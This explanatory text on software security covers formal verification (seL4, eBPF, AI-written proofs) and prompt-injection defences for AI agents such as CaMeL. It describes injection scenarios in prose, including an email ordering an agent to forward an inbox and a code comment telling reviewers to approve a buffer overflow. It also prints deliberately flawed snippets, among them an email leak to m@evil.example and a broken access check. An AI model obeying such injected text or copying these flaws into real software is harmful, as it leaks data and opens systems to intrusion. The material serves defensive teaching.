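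Even so, Keel's guarantee depends on the C compiler, a model of how the kernel behaves, and the eBPF verifier, which still writes the conditions. A fault in the verifier could produce the wrong condition, just as a fault in Necula and Lee's generator could. *Proof-Carrying Verification for eBPF* (Fink, 2026) proposes moving all the search out of the kernel. Suppliers would provide the loop invariants, and a checker would only confirm them. An early prototype handles some eBPF programs. An older project with a similar aim shut down after its proofs turned out to be very large.

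*Approximation Enforced Execution of Untrusted Linux Kernel Extensions* adds run-time checks that stop a program if a value leaves the range the verifier predicted, so a wrong prediction doesn't expose the kernel. The checks take some time, which proof-carrying code was meant to save.

### Safe according to the policy

A proof guarantees only what the policy covers. A packet filter that throws away every packet would satisfy Necula and Lee's policy. Most policies in use similarly cover memory and perhaps running time, but not whether the program does its job.

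Dasu and colleagues found nine bugs in widely used eBPF programs that the verifier had accepted. One program, which records the commands that people type, fills in only the start of an 84-byte record but sends out all 84 bytes, including whatever the kernel had left in the rest. This leftover data revealed the kernel's randomized location in memory. The verifier's policy deliberately allows privileged programs to send out such data.

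In another program, the developers used the number 2 to let network packets through. It means that at one point in the kernel's network code, but where this program ran, it means "drop the packet". A third program, in Meta's load balancer, used `=` instead of `==`, so it changed a value it was supposed to compare.

A stricter policy can catch some of these bugs without any knowledge of a program's purpose. For example, Dasu and colleagues require a program to fill in every byte it sends out, which any correct program should do anyway. But somebody has to write and maintain such rules. Fink considers this a central problem for eBPF, because the policy must cover every kernel function a program can call and must change whenever those functions do.

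The thumbnail service could likewise extend its policy to require that a brightness routine finish within 10,000 instructions and return a number from 0 to 255. The altered routine that always returns 0 would still pass, and every thumbnail would come out black. To exclude it, the developers would have to define what the right brightness is.

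## Proving whole programs and reviewing the specification instead

Necula and Lee's policies covered little more than memory, but a proof can cover everything a program is supposed to do. A program is *functionally correct* if, in every situation, it does only what its specification allows. The best-known program proved functionally correct is seL4, an operating system kernel from a research group in Sydney now called Trustworthy Systems.

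### How the seL4 proof works

seL4 is a *microkernel*, a kernel that does only the few jobs no ordinary process could safely do, such as dividing up memory and passing messages. Files, networking and most device drivers run outside it. According to *seL4*, the paper that announced the proof in 2009, the kernel has 8,700 lines of C and 600 of assembly code.

The specification describes what each operation does but not how. The proof shows that every step of the C code corresponds to a step that the specification allows. The same method would work for the list of videos waiting at the thumbnail service. In its specification, "add" puts a video at the end of the list and "take" removes the first. The C program stores the videos in an array of 100 slots and records the position of the oldest video and how many are waiting.

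To connect the two, the developers define a relation R. R(a, c) holds if the slots in the C program's state c, read in order from the oldest, contain exactly the list a. They then prove for each operation:

if R(a, c) holds and the C program can go from c to c′, then the specification allows a step from a to some a′ for which R(a′, c′) holds

If this is true of every operation, and R holds at the start, then the array matches the list after any number of operations in any order. But in this program the proof of "add" fails. When 100 videos are waiting, adding another overwrites the oldest, and no array of 100 slots can match a list of 101. The developers have to fix the program, perhaps by refusing the extra video and adding the refusal to the specification. They find the fault without having to imagine an attacker who uploads 101 videos at once.

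The seL4 proof implies that the kernel never crashes and never performs an unsafe operation. It originally depended on the compiler, the assembly code and the hardware being correct. Researchers later extended it to the compiled machine code, so the compiler no longer had to be trusted. Trustworthy Systems says the proof covers 7,500 lines of the kernel's C code but not the code that starts the kernel.

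The proof is 200,000 lines long, or about 27 lines for each line of C it covers. People wrote it by hand, and a proof assistant called Isabelle checks it. The whole project took about 25 person-years. Heiser (2009), one of its leaders, attributes 12 of these to the kernel's proof and 10 to general tools for proving things about C. The usual figure of 20 person-years is for the proof alone. The first version of the C code took two weeks to write. Heiser estimated that, because the tools now existed, a second project of this kind would take 6 person-years, compared with 4 to 6 for conventional engineering.

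Testing had found 16 bugs in the kernel, and the proof found another 160 in the C code. Experience with CompCert, a C compiler with a similar proof, also suggests that proofs find what testing misses. Researchers quoted on the seL4 project's website spent about six years of processor time compiling random programs, and found bugs in the middle stages of every compiler they tried except CompCert.

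### A helicopter with hackers on board

DARPA's HACMS programme tested seL4 and formal methods against professional attackers. DARPA's *HACMS* describes how a red team of hired hackers first took control of a small quadcopter and then of the Little Bird, an unmanned helicopter that its Boeing engineers had believed was immune to attack. The hackers broke into one of the helicopter's computers and from there easily reached the one that controlled its flight.

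On the quadcopter, the defenders rewrote about 80,000 of 100,000 lines using formal methods and divided the software into partitions. They then applied the same approach to the helicopter, where Boeing's engineers did most of the work. seL4 kept the partitions apart and allowed only the communication the design specified. Much of the software inside the partitions had no proof.

The red team had six weeks to break into the helicopter, and failed. According to Cofer (2018), the team had the source code, the binaries and all the design documents, so the defenders weren't relying on secrecy. DARPA then gave the attackers control of the partition that ran the camera. They couldn't break out of it, even when the defenders repeated the test in flight with two pilots on board.

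DARPA says the attackers were "mathematically guaranteed" to stay in the camera partition. That is true only if the hardware works as the proof assumes and the engineers correctly specified which partitions may communicate. The red team's failure is useful evidence about these assumptions, because the proof can't test them. It is weaker evidence about the proof itself, since a carefully built kernel without a proof might also have survived six weeks.

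Isolation also can't stop an attack that uses a permitted channel. *UAV Resilience Against Stealthy Attacks* (2025) discusses security flaws in MAVLink, a protocol for controlling drones, and presents an attack model that threatens the HACMS approach. If a partition is allowed to steer the aircraft and acts on a forged command, the kernel does not intervene.

### Why correctness rules out takeovers

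Some advocates of formal proof argue that functional correctness brings resistance to takeovers at no extra cost. Let S be the set of behaviours that a program's specification allows. The argument has four steps:

1. A proof shows that everything the program can do is in S.
2. S excludes at least one behaviour, B, that code on this machine could produce.
3. If attackers could run arbitrary code in the program, they could run code that does B.
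4. The program could then do something outside S, which contradicts step 1. So attackers can't run arbitrary code in it.

The specification for an internet service that adds positive numbers might say only that every answer is positive. An attacker who could run arbitrary code could make the service answer 0, so a proof that it never does rules out that degree of control. The specification doesn't mention buffer overflows or any other technique, but the proof covers them all, including those nobody has invented yet, so reviewers don't have to anticipate which one an attacker might use to gain that control.

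The reasoning is valid, but it rules out less than it seems to. Here is a very badly designed version of the service:

```
result = run_sealed(code_from_request)
if result < 1:
    result = 1
send(result)
```

The service runs whatever code the request contains, sealed off so that the code can only read the service's memory and return a number. Every answer is positive, so the service meets its specification. The attacker doesn't have *arbitrary* control, because they can't make it send 0, but they can make it return a stored password encoded as a large positive number.

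If the specification gave the exact sum for every request, this service would fail the proof, because a password isn't the sum of the customer's numbers. Even then, an attacker could use the processor to mine cryptocurrency before sending the right answer, unless the specification also limited running time. An attacker with partial control can do only as much harm as the specification allows.

Specifications often leave such room deliberately. Suppose a thumbnail file has 16 bytes reserved for future use, and the specification says they may contain anything. A program that fills them with part of another customer's video is functionally correct. To exclude this, the developers have to prove a different kind of property, called *noninterference*:

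if two runs differ only in other customers' data, this customer receives the same output in both

Researchers later proved a property like this for seL4. It rules out leaks through anything modeled as output, but models usually leave out how long the output takes.

A functionally correct program can still leak secrets through its timing. Suppose a function compares a password with the stored one letter by letter and stops at the first mismatch. It always gives the right answer, but it takes slightly longer when the first letter is right, so an attacker can find that letter in at most 26 tries and then move on to the next. A password of eight lower-case letters has about 209 billion possibilities, but this method needs at most 208 guesses, apart from repeated measurements to average out noise. A specification can require that the sequence of instructions never depends on the password. Whether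 the function then takes the same time for every password depends on the hardware.

### From test programs to proofs

In October 2026 Anthropic and the company Theorem showed that AI can write such proofs for software that wasn't designed to be verified. Anthropic's *LLMs are making formal software verification feasible at a much larger scale* (2026) argues that verification no longer requires the years of expert effort that made it impractical for most projects.

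The project started from OSS-Fuzz, Google's service for fuzzing open-source software. Each library there comes with small test programs that take a block of bytes and pass it to some of the library's functions. Anthropic and Theorem turned the tests into specifications of this form:

for every input x smaller than 64 MB, the test program exits normally when it runs on x

EconoTimes' *Anthropic Details Claude's No-Crash Proofs for 239 Fuzz-Test Entry Points* (2026) explains that "normally" means without a crash, a memory error or a failed assertion. A proof covers every such input. There are more than 2 to the power of 500 million of them, so testing 100 billion, as the Bun team did on its parsers, would cover a negligible fraction.

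Claude, Anthropic's AI model, proved the property for 239 test programs from 123 libraries. The proofs are in the language of Rocq, another proof assistant, and total about 180 million lines, or 900 times the length of the original seL4 proof. OpenNET's *Аnthropic развивает технику для формальной верификации существующего ПО при помощи AI* (2026) reports that a binary with 18,000 instructions needed about 600,000 lines of proof. Because the proofs are about compiled machine code, nobody had to rewrite the libraries or trust a compiler.

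A program with a reachable crash can't be proved crash-free, so attempting the proof also exposes bugs. Claude found and fixed hundreds that fuzzing had missed, including a buffer overflow in libexpat, a widely used XML parser. Some of the guarantees therefore apply only to the corrected versions of the programs.

Proving that a program does its job is much harder than proving that it never crashes, and the project also attempted the harder task twice. Claude proved that the Linux kernel's implementation of zlib, a compression format, matches the published standard. It also wrote a Rust interpreter for part of Python, with a proof that the interpreter follows a formal description of the language. To check this description, the researchers ran 1.7 million random programs in both the new interpreter and CPython, the standard one. The results agreed for 99.95 percent of the programs, and the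 rest were known edge cases.

The 239 guarantees cover only what the test programs do, so an application that calls a library's functions in another order, or calls functions that the tests never use, has no guarantee. The binaries are for RISC-V, an open processor design that is still rare in servers and phones. The model has only one thread and leaves out dynamic linking (loading shared libraries when a program starts) and hardware faults. The size limit would also be a problem for a thumbnail service, since a minute of video from a modern phone often exceeds 64 MB. Most video decoders also use several threads, which the model does not cover.

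Other projects have already got past some of these limits:

- Leip (2026), in *Announcing Zellic's and V12's Work on x86 Binary Formal Verification*, reports a proof about a complete Linux program for x86, the family of processors in most servers. It includes the standard C library, which ordinary programs rely on.
- Chaudhuri, Ferraiuolo and colleagues (2026), in *AlphaProof Code*, describe proofs by Google DeepMind's AI agents about libsignal, the code that encrypts messages in the Signal app. They use a model of AArch64, the processor design in most phones.
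- Kaashoek (2026) presents a proof about xv6, a small teaching operating system, on a model with eight RISC-V processors. The theorem covers every order in which the processors, devices, interrupts and power cuts can affect one another.

Besides ruling out crashes, the Signal proofs show, for example, that someone who steals a user's current keys can't decrypt past messages, and that a conversation can become secure again after a break-in. Cryptographers had proved such properties of protocols on paper, but Chaudhuri and colleagues are the first to connect them to the unmodified code of a widely used implementation.

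### What people still have to read

The Signal proofs run to about 6.5 million lines, which the proof assistant Lean checks. They rest on about 26,000 lines of specifications and processor description that people have to trust, or one line for every 250 lines of proof. The reviewer has to check whether the specifications require the right thing and whether the processor description matches the actual processor.

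The model is the easier of the two to review. Its definitions are public, many projects can share them, and engineers can run the same instructions on the model and on a real chip to compare the results. As with taming Java's libraries, the work is slow, but a team needs to do it only once for each processor.

But even a model that matches the manual exactly can differ from the hardware. In 2014, researchers showed that rapidly reading one row of a memory chip many thousands of times can flip bits in neighbouring rows. Within a year, Google's engineers had used this effect, called Rowhammer, to take over a Linux kernel. A model in which memory always keeps what a program writes there can't represent this attack. A proof based on that model would still be valid, but it wouldn't describe the real machine.

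Reviewing a specification is easiest when somebody has already stated the requirements exactly. Microsoft's *Verifying Rust cryptography in SymCrypt, from standards to code* describes how the company's engineers turn a published cryptographic standard into a formal specification and prove that Rust code matches it, with AI agents helping to write the proofs. A reviewer can compare that specification with the standard line by line, but most of what ordinary software does has no comparable standard.

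For the thumbnail service, a specification might include this rule:

if the service sends thumbnail t to customer c, then t shows a frame of some stored video that belongs to c

A proof of this rule would guarantee that the service never sends one customer a picture from another customer's video, which none of the earlier methods could fully guarantee. However, because the rule's wording is "some stored video", the service could answer a request for a picture from a birthday party video with a frame from a medical scan if the same customer had uploaded both. The rule also forbids the service from showing a thumbnail to a colleague the customer has shared the video with. Someone who knows what customers expect could notice both mistakes without knowing anything about hacking.

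### Proved programs that went wrong

Mistakes in specifications are common. Besides the 160 bugs in seL4's C code, Heiser counts about 150 in its design and another 150 in its specification. The researchers found these because the specification contradicted the code or itself, or made something impossible to prove. They would not have found a mistake that the code and the specification shared.

Wi-Fi is a serious example of a missing requirement. A device joining a network exchanges four messages with the access point to agree on an encryption key. Researchers had proved that this exchange keeps the key secret. In 2017 Mathy Vanhoef and Frank Piessens found that an attacker could make a device reinstall the same key by replaying the third message. Each reinstallation reset the counter that should give every packet a new number, so the device encrypted different packets the same way, and the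 attacker could often decrypt them. The attack didn't contradict the proof, because the key stayed secret. The proof's model didn't include installing the key, so nobody had required that a device install it only once.

Other failures come from code that a proof relies on but doesn't cover. *Lean proved this program was correct; then I found a bug* describes fuzzing a zlib implementation that had a proof in Lean and finding a buffer overflow in Lean's runtime, which every compiled Lean program needs to run. The Ethereum Foundation examines a similar misunderstanding about SP1 Hypercube, which produces cryptographic evidence that a program ran correctly. Its developers had announced a proof covering its "entire core", but the system still had a bug. The foundation argues that even a narrower guarantee is useful because it shows security experts which parts to concentrate on.

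Customers may find it hard to tell which parts a proof covers. Symbolic Software (2026) reports six vulnerabilities in software from a company that sells formally verified cryptography. The worst two were in hpke-rs, an encryption library that Signal depends on, and one caused the library to reuse one-time numbers, much as the Wi-Fi devices did. Symbolic Software says it also found bugs in the verified code. It is in a bitter dispute with the company, which questioned its good faith but, by Symbolic Software's account, later merged its fixes.

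*Formal Verification is Not Verifiable* (Keles, 2026) argues that people should stop saying "formally verified software" and name the properties that have been proved. In the past, a proof took years of work by researchers whose reputations depended on it, so readers could assume that it wasn't about something trivial. Other researchers then reviewed it and built on it, and still found bugs. An AI system can produce proofs far faster than people can judge whether the theorems are worth proving.

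An AI prover might also get a proof accepted by weakening the specification. Chaudhuri and colleagues prevent this by using separate agents to write the specification and search for proofs. The first agent writes the specification under human guidance, and the others must prove exactly what people approved. Software can check that they did, but approving the specification takes human judgment.

Developers can test a specification by planting a known bug in the program. If the proof still succeeds, the specification is too weak to exclude that bug. This test takes little effort and is worth doing, but it reveals only the gaps that correspond to the planted bugs. Choosing the right bugs takes some of the imagination that the proof was supposed to make unnecessary.

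### Will proofs scale?

Well before the 2026 results, several people expected proofs to become practical for large systems. Drexler expects advanced AI to make secure, verified software affordable on a large scale. Tegmark and Steve Omohundro argued in 2023 that proof is the only reliable way to control AI systems much more capable than people. David Dalrymple (davidad) and colleagues proposed a design in which an AI system must use a mathematical model of the world to prove that its actions meet a safety specification.

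All of them rely on an untrusted AI to find the proofs and a simple checker to catch its mistakes. Kleppmann (2025), in *Prediction*, argues for the same approach in ordinary software, and would rather have a language model prove its code correct than have people review it.

The objections to proving whole programs concern cost, requirements and the physical world. *How Could Formal Verification Help with Cyber Resilience?* considers verifying widely used programs of under 200,000 lines realistic, but calls verifying projects of more than a million lines a high-risk bet. It also expects organisational inertia to slow adoption even if AI makes proofs cheap. Tolmach and Klaus (2026), in *The proof is in the spec*, say the bottleneck has moved from finding proofs to writing specifications and choosing the right model. They work for a company that sells such expertise, but the failures in Wi-Fi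 and SP1 Hypercube support their claim.

Results from 2026 have greatly weakened the objection about cost, at least for small programs. The 2009 proof of one 8,700-line kernel took a team of specialists many years, while an AI model can now prove a simpler property for 123 existing libraries. Galois' *You Can't Patch Your Way Out of This* concludes that if AI can automate proofs, security may no longer depend on racing to patch vulnerabilities. Galois sells formal verification, and its conclusion goes further than the evidence for large programs. A browser has tens of millions of lines, many threads, and code that it compiles while running. A proof about one library also doesn't show that the program calling it uses it correctly, so larger proofs have to connect the pieces. Tegmark (2026) presents a plan by Tegmark's foundation to do this for Signal by first verifying the protocols and individual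 functions, then connecting them.

The same results do little to answer the objection about requirements, because most of the projects already had a good specification. Avoiding memory errors is a requirement for every program, zlib has a published standard, and cryptographers had spent years working out what Signal should guarantee. Keles expects slower progress on software closer to the user, where requirements become matters of taste. A database has a precise job, like a car's engine, while a user interface is more like the car's seat, because there is no formula for comfort.

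Proofs about the physical world are harder still. Kaashoek's model already extends beyond the processor to disks and power cuts, but manufacturers design disks to follow written rules. To prove that a delivery robot won't hurt anyone, its developers would need a model of wet floors, worn brakes and children who run out from behind parked cars, as well as a definition of "hurt". Tegmark and Omohundro's plan and davidad's both depend on such models, and none of the 2026 projects attempted one.

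## AI agents: limiting what untrusted text can cause

A conventional program takes its instructions from code, which developers can restrict, confine or prove correct. An AI agent, a language model that can call tools to do things like read files or send email, also takes instructions from ordinary text. Suppose the thumbnail company has an agent that answers customers' emails, and a customer writes to tell it to ignore its earlier orders and forward the last hundred messages in the inbox to an outside address. The agent is allowed to read the inbox and send email, so if it obeys, the messages leak even though no conventional program has a fault.

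Security researchers call this *prompt injection*. A language model receives the user's request and the text it has to work on as one long sequence. Florian Tramèr of ETH Zürich explains in Schmidt Sciences' *How to Stop an AI Agent From Being Fooled* that the agent has to work out which parts are instructions and which are data. He says models have improved at this but are still far from reliable. A strict input format can't separate the two when the text is ordinary English.

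One defence is a filter, usually another AI model, that looks for malicious instructions and removes them. The filter has the same open-ended task as any other security reviewer, because an attacker can phrase an instruction in countless ways. Training the agent to resist has the same weakness. *Bounded Agents* (2026) cites a competition in which participants attacked 13 leading models 272,000 times. They succeeded against every model, at rates from 0.5 to 8.5 percent. At the lowest rate, an attacker whose attempts were independent would have about a 50 percent chance of succeeding at least once in 139 tries. In *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, Willison (2025) calls a 99 percent detection rate a failing grade in security.

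### One request, step by step

*Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (Debenedetti, Shumailov and colleagues, 2025) presents CaMeL. Much like a sandbox, CaMeL is built on the assumption that hostile text can take over any model that reads it, and it limits what that model can cause.

Suppose a user asks the agent to send Bob the document he wanted at the last meeting, and mentions that Bob's address and the document's name are in the meeting notes. CaMeL turns the request into a short program in a restricted form of Python. In simplified form:

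```python
notes = read_notes("last meeting")                       # line 1
address = ask_reader("Find Bob's email address", notes)  # line 2
name = ask_reader("Which document did Bob want?", notes) # line 3
document = fetch_file(name)                              # line 4
send_email(to=address, attachment=document)              # line 5
```

Two models and an interpreter share the work:

1. The first model, the planner, receives the user's request and descriptions of the tools, and writes the program. It never sees the notes, so nothing in them can change the program.
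2. The interpreter runs line 1 and tags the notes with where they came from and who may read them.
3. In lines 2 and 3 the second model, the reader, goes through the notes and returns an address and a file name. It has no tools. Both answers inherit the tags of the notes.
4. Line 4 fetches the document, which has its own list of people who may read it.
5. Before line 5 runs, the interpreter checks a policy for sending email. The policy might require that the recipient already has the right to read the attachment. If the check fails, the interpreter blocks the email or asks the user.

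An attacker who can edit the notes might add an order to send every file on the drive to an outside address. Even if the order changes the reader's output, the reader can only return a wrong address or a wrong file name. If it returns the attacker's address, the policy blocks the email because the attacker isn't allowed to read the document. Willison proposed a design with the same two models in 2023, but it lacked the tags, so substituting the attacker's address would have defeated it.

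CaMeL's designers call the tags capabilities, but the tags are labels on data, not references that grant access as capabilities do in a capability-safe language. Comparing the tags with a policy is a narrow task, and no wording in the notes can change a tag.

### What the protection costs

The usual test for such systems is *AgentDojo* (2024), which has 97 ordinary tasks in four simulated settings: a bank, a travel agency, an office and the messaging service Slack. It also has 629 security tests, which hide an attacker's instructions in the data the agent reads. In a later version of their paper, Debenedetti and colleagues report that CaMeL solved 77 percent of the tasks with its guarantees in place, compared with 84 percent for an undefended system.

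Results depend heavily on the model and the set-up. *Indirect Prompt Injections* (Bhagwatkar, Kasa and colleagues, 2025) quotes CaMeL's published results with GPT-4o, an older model. No attack succeeded against CaMeL, and it solved 53.6 percent of the tasks, compared with 83.0 percent in the paper's own undefended runs. CaMeL also used 2.82 times as many input tokens (the word fragments that models process and users pay for) and 2.73 times as many output tokens. *SecureClaw* (2026) reports a run of the full benchmark in which none of the 629 attacks succeeded, but CaMeL solved only 29 of the 97 tasks.

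Much of the loss comes from the policies. *Language-Based Agent Control* (2026) reports that CaMeL, run with four recent models, solved 13 to 17 of the 21 Slack tasks with the policies off and 4 to 6 with them on. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *The LLMbda Calculus*, found that the policies halved CaMeL's success on the banking tasks. Many tasks require the agent to act on something it has read, such as paying a bill in a file, and a strict policy forbids this. In a real product the interpreter could ask the user to approve the payment, so these figures partly measure how often CaMeL would have to interrupt the user.

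AgentDojo isn't a severe test of security. Garby and colleagues examined its 144 combinations of banking task and attack, and found that 97 need a tool that would never appear in a plan for the task. Separating the planner from the reader is enough to block those 97, even without a policy. Bhagwatkar and colleagues used a language model to clean each tool's output, which stopped every attack on AgentDojo, and the agent still solved 74 percent of the tasks. They take this partly as a sign that the benchmark's attacks are too weak.

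*The Devil is in the Context* (2026) tested defenses on newly generated cases. CaMeL let through 2.5 percent of the attacks and solved 27.5 percent of the tasks, while PromptArmor, a filter, let through 7.5 percent and solved 90 percent. All the percentages are multiples of 2.5, which suggests about 40 cases, so the difference in security could be one successful attack versus three. On this evidence, a filter is the better choice against ordinary attacks, but it offers no guarantee against someone who keeps rewriting a message until the filter passes it.

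### Simpler designs

An agent with a limited job may not need CaMeL. *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues, 2025) describes six patterns based on the principle that once a model has read untrusted text, that text must not be able to trigger any action with harmful side effects.

| Pattern | What it forbids | What hostile text can still do |
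|---|---|---|
| Action selector | The model picks from a fixed list of actions and never sees their results | Nothing through the results, though a hostile request can pick the wrong action |
| Plan, then execute | Text the agent reads can't add actions to a plan it has already made | Change the content of an email the plan sends |
| Map-reduce | A separate model reads each document and may return only something simple, such as yes or no | Get its own document misjudged |
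| Dual model | The model with tools never sees untrusted text | Supply false values |
| Code, then execute (CaMeL) | As above, with the plan written as a program that an interpreter can check | Supply false values that the policy allows |
| Context minimisation | The system deletes the user's words before the model writes its reply | Influence whatever the system extracted from those words first |

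Suppose an agent has to find this month's invoices and email them to the accounts department. With map-reduce, one model reads each file and answers only whether it is an invoice. An attacker can get a malicious file classified as an invoice, which they could have done anyway by writing a fake one, but they can't use it to make the agent send other files.

The patterns work by making agents less general. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues doubt that anyone can give reliable guarantees for a general-purpose agent built on the current kind of language model. A support agent that only directs customers to the right page loses nothing by using the first pattern, but an assistant meant to handle any request from its owner can't use it.

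### When the next step depends on the text

A CaMeL planner has to write the whole program before anyone has read the data. The program can include branches for situations the planner foresees, but it can't add a step if a tool returns something unexpected. In *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026) tested CaMeL on teams of agents and found that this limitation caused most of the failures on ordinary tasks. On 112 industrial maintenance tasks, with no policies in force, CaMeL lowered the success rate by an average of 21.6 percentage points across five models. Better models seem to foresee more of what might happen, and the average loss for the two strongest, Fable 5 and GPT-5.5, was 13.4 points.

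The problem is worse for agents that operate a computer by looking at its screen. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues, 2026) had the planner prepare for every likely screen in advance. The plans averaged 41 tool calls and 40 branches, compared with about five tool calls and four branches on AgentDojo, and about half of each plan was fallbacks that never ran. The agents kept up to 57 percent of the performance of leading models that can look at the screen before each action.

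Some requests require the agent to obey whatever a text says. One AgentDojo task tells the agent to read a file and follow its instructions precisely. When Garby and colleagues ran CaMeL on this task without policies, the planner wrote a loop that read each instruction in the file and called whichever tool it named. The loop was a sensible way to do what the user asked, but it let anyone who could edit the file use all those tools.

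*Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (2026) presents TACIT, a system in which a single model reads untrusted text and writes code as it goes, without planning in advance. A type checker rejects code that would send protected data somewhere it shouldn't go. TACIT blocked all but one of the attacks on AgentDojo and solved about as many tasks as CaMeL. But any instruction the model reads can mislead it, so the protection depends entirely on the type rules.

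### When one agent instructs another

Companies increasingly divide work among several agents, and CaMeL's guarantee can fail when one agent passes a message to another. Peters-Gill and colleagues asked a coordinating agent to send Julie a summary of some job applications on Slack. It got the applications from a database agent, had a reader summarise them, and included the summary in a request telling a third agent to send it to Julie. An attacker had planted an instruction in the database, and it survived into the summary. The first two agents treated the instruction as data, but the third received it as part of its user's request, and its planner added a step that emailed the applicants' details to an outsider.

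All three agents were running CaMeL correctly. The remedy is to send the instruction and the summary separately and keep the summary hidden from the next planner. In tests with 949 attacks per model, the average success rate fell from 12.9 percent without CaMeL to 0.2 percent with ordinary CaMeL, and to zero with separate channels. Most of the successful attacks on undefended agents were against older models. None of the 949 succeeded against GPT-5.5, even with no defence, although Peters-Gill and colleagues warn that a more determined attacker might still succeed.

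### False values in permitted places

An attacker can also supply false information without changing the plan. In Bob's case, the notes could name an out-of-date contract that Bob has the right to read. Bob would then receive the wrong contract, even though the address is correct and the policy is satisfied.

Garby and colleagues built an agent that always tracks where its data came from but can explicitly mark a piece of untrusted data as acceptable for a particular use. It solved about twice as many banking tasks as CaMeL with policies, and attacks succeeded in only two of 1,296 attacked runs. In both, the user had asked the agent to read a file and make the payment it described, and the attacker had replaced the file with a fraudulent bill. Tracking could show that the payment details came from the file, but the user had told the agent to take them from there. To stop the attack, the agent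 would have had to recognise the bill as suspicious or refuse to pay any bill from a file.

Foerster and colleagues show a similar attack on the screen-reading agent. Its plans usually include a step for closing cookie notices, since many websites have them. An attacker can disguise an advertisement as a cookie notice, so that the agent clicks it and lands on a malicious site. The attack doesn't change the plan, and a policy can't easily forbid the click, because clicking the same point on the screen can be harmless on one page and harmful on another.

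### Writing the rules and approving the exceptions

Someone has to write CaMeL's policies and keep them up to date. *Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems* (2026) compares two ways to stop an agent from emailing secrets. One assigns secrecy levels to files and limits what the agent may read. The other allows all reading, but blocks email once the agent has read both sensitive data and text from an untrusted source. Both stopped all five attempted thefts, while telling the model not to leak data stopped none. People can write rules like these without knowing about particular attacks, but they have to know which data are sensitive and what the agent's work requires.

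Some rules concern the order of events. *CaMeLoT* (Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of an agent that may disconnect a computer from a company's network only after the incident team approves. CaMeL checks each action only when the agent reaches it, so it might discover a missing approval after hours of other work. CaMeLoT runs a model checker over every path through the program before execution starts. If a path lacks the approval, the planner receives that path and can add the step.

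Policies also depend on accurate tags. Garby and colleagues found that CaMeL could lose track of a secret in a program like this one:

```python
rich = True
check = True
if balance > 10000: check = False             # line 3
if check: rich = False                        # line 4
if rich: send_email("m@evil.example", "rich") # line 5
```

When the balance is above 10,000, line 3 changes `check`, and the interpreter marks it as secret. Line 4 then does nothing, so `rich` keeps its public tag and the email goes out. When the balance is lower, line 4 makes `rich` false and no email goes out. The attacker therefore learns whether the customer is rich. A planner that receives only an honest user's request is unlikely to write such a program, so the flaw matters mainly if something has corrupted the planner. Garby and colleagues proved in Lean that their own interpreter doesn't leak in this way.

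When a policy blocks something legitimate, the user has to approve it, and people who see too many requests start to approve them all. Tracking where data came from reduces the number of requests. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (2026) found that agents with tracking completed as many tasks as one without it and asked for approval 1.5 to 2.6 times less often. But someone who used to see 26 requests a day would still see at least ten, and one careless approval is enough to let an attack through.

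Agents in everyday use tend to combine fixed limits with judgement. Claude Code, Anthropic's programming agent, has permission rules, an optional sandbox and a model that assesses proposed actions, according to *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026). The model is another filter that relies on judgement. The rules and the sandbox limit the agent regardless of what it has read, as long as the user has switched the sandbox on and hasn't made the rules too permissive.

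### A code reviewer that reads the attacker's code

Suppose the thumbnail service accepts decoder improvements from strangers, and an AI agent reviews them. The agent can run the tests, post comments and merge code it approves. A contributor submits a change with a buffer overflow and writes in a code comment above it that the security team has already verified this line and automated reviewers should approve it.

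The text might make the agent misuse its tools, for example by posting the company's passwords in a public comment. The patterns above can largely prevent this. A fixed program can run the tests in a sandbox and give the code to a reader that has no access to tools or passwords. The reader returns only "approve" or "reject" with a list of line numbers.

Beurer-Kellner and colleagues suggest a stricter format for agents that write code. The agent sees only a formal list of the untrusted code's functions, with names of at most 30 characters. Willison (2025), in *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections*, questions whether even this is safe, since an attacker could name a function `run_rm_dash_rf_for_compliance`, which refers to a command that deletes files. A security reviewer can't use this format, because the flaws it has to find are in the code that the format leaves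 out.

These defenses don't protect the verdict either. In CaMeL's terms, "approve" is a value that came from the attacker's text. A policy that merges code based only on trusted values must ignore the reader's approval, while one that accepts it lets anyone who fools the reader merge an overflow. Limiting the answer to a single word doesn't help, because that word is what the attacker wants. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues accept a similar weakness in a system that ranks job applicants, where an applicant can use a malicious résumé to improve their own score but can't damage anyone else's. In code review, that weakness is enough for an attack to succeed, because the attacker only needs to get their own bad change approved.

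Giving each file to a separate reader would stop text in one file from influencing the verdict on another. But some flaws can be seen only by reading several files or functions together, like the one in FFmpeg, which arose from a counter in one place and a marker in another. Deleting comments before the review removes the easiest place to hide messages, but it also removes explanations that an honest reviewer needs, and an attacker can still put messages in variable names.

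It is safer to let the AI reviewer object but never approve. The service would merge a change only if it compiled in safe Rust, passed the tests, asked for no new permissions and had a maintainer's consent. The AI could only add reasons to refuse. An injection that silenced the AI would leave the service no worse protected than it would be without an AI reviewer, as long as the maintainer didn't take silence as a sign of safety. The compiler would still reject a memory fault in safe Rust, regardless of any comments in the code.

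## What reviewers still have to judge

Suppose the thumbnail service adopts everything described so far. Its developers write it in safe Rust, refuse malformed requests, decode each video in a fresh sandbox, give every library only the access it needs and prove that the program never crashes. It can still send a customer a picture from somebody else's video, if the developers write this:

```rust
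fn get_thumbnail(request: &Request, login: &Login, store: &Store) -> Option<Picture> {
    login.check_active()?;                      // line 1
    let video = store.find(request.video_id)?;  // line 2
    if video.owner != request.customer_id {     // line 3
        return None;
    }
    Some(decode_in_sandbox(video))              // line 4
}
```

Line 1 checks that the customer is logged in, and line 2 finds the video. Line 3 should reject anyone except the owner, but it compares the owner with the customer number in the request, which the sender can set to any number. Customer 12 can log in, ask for video 812 and put 57, the owner's customer number, in the request. The two numbers match, so customer 12 receives the picture.

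The compiler accepts this code because every memory access is legal. The request is well formed. The sandbox decodes one video and returns the correct picture of it. The function needs access to the whole store because it serves every customer, and it never crashes.

This is a *logic bug*, a fault in which every operation is legal but the program breaks its intended rules. Trying to prove that customers receive only frames from their own videos would expose it, but somebody has to write that rule first. *No Room for Bugs* (Hellerstein, 2026) distinguishes universal properties, which every program should have, from arbitrary ones, which are specific to a single program. Memory safety is universal, so a language designer can enforce it without knowing what a program is for. "Every voter can only vote once" is arbitrary, and so is the rule about customers and their videos.

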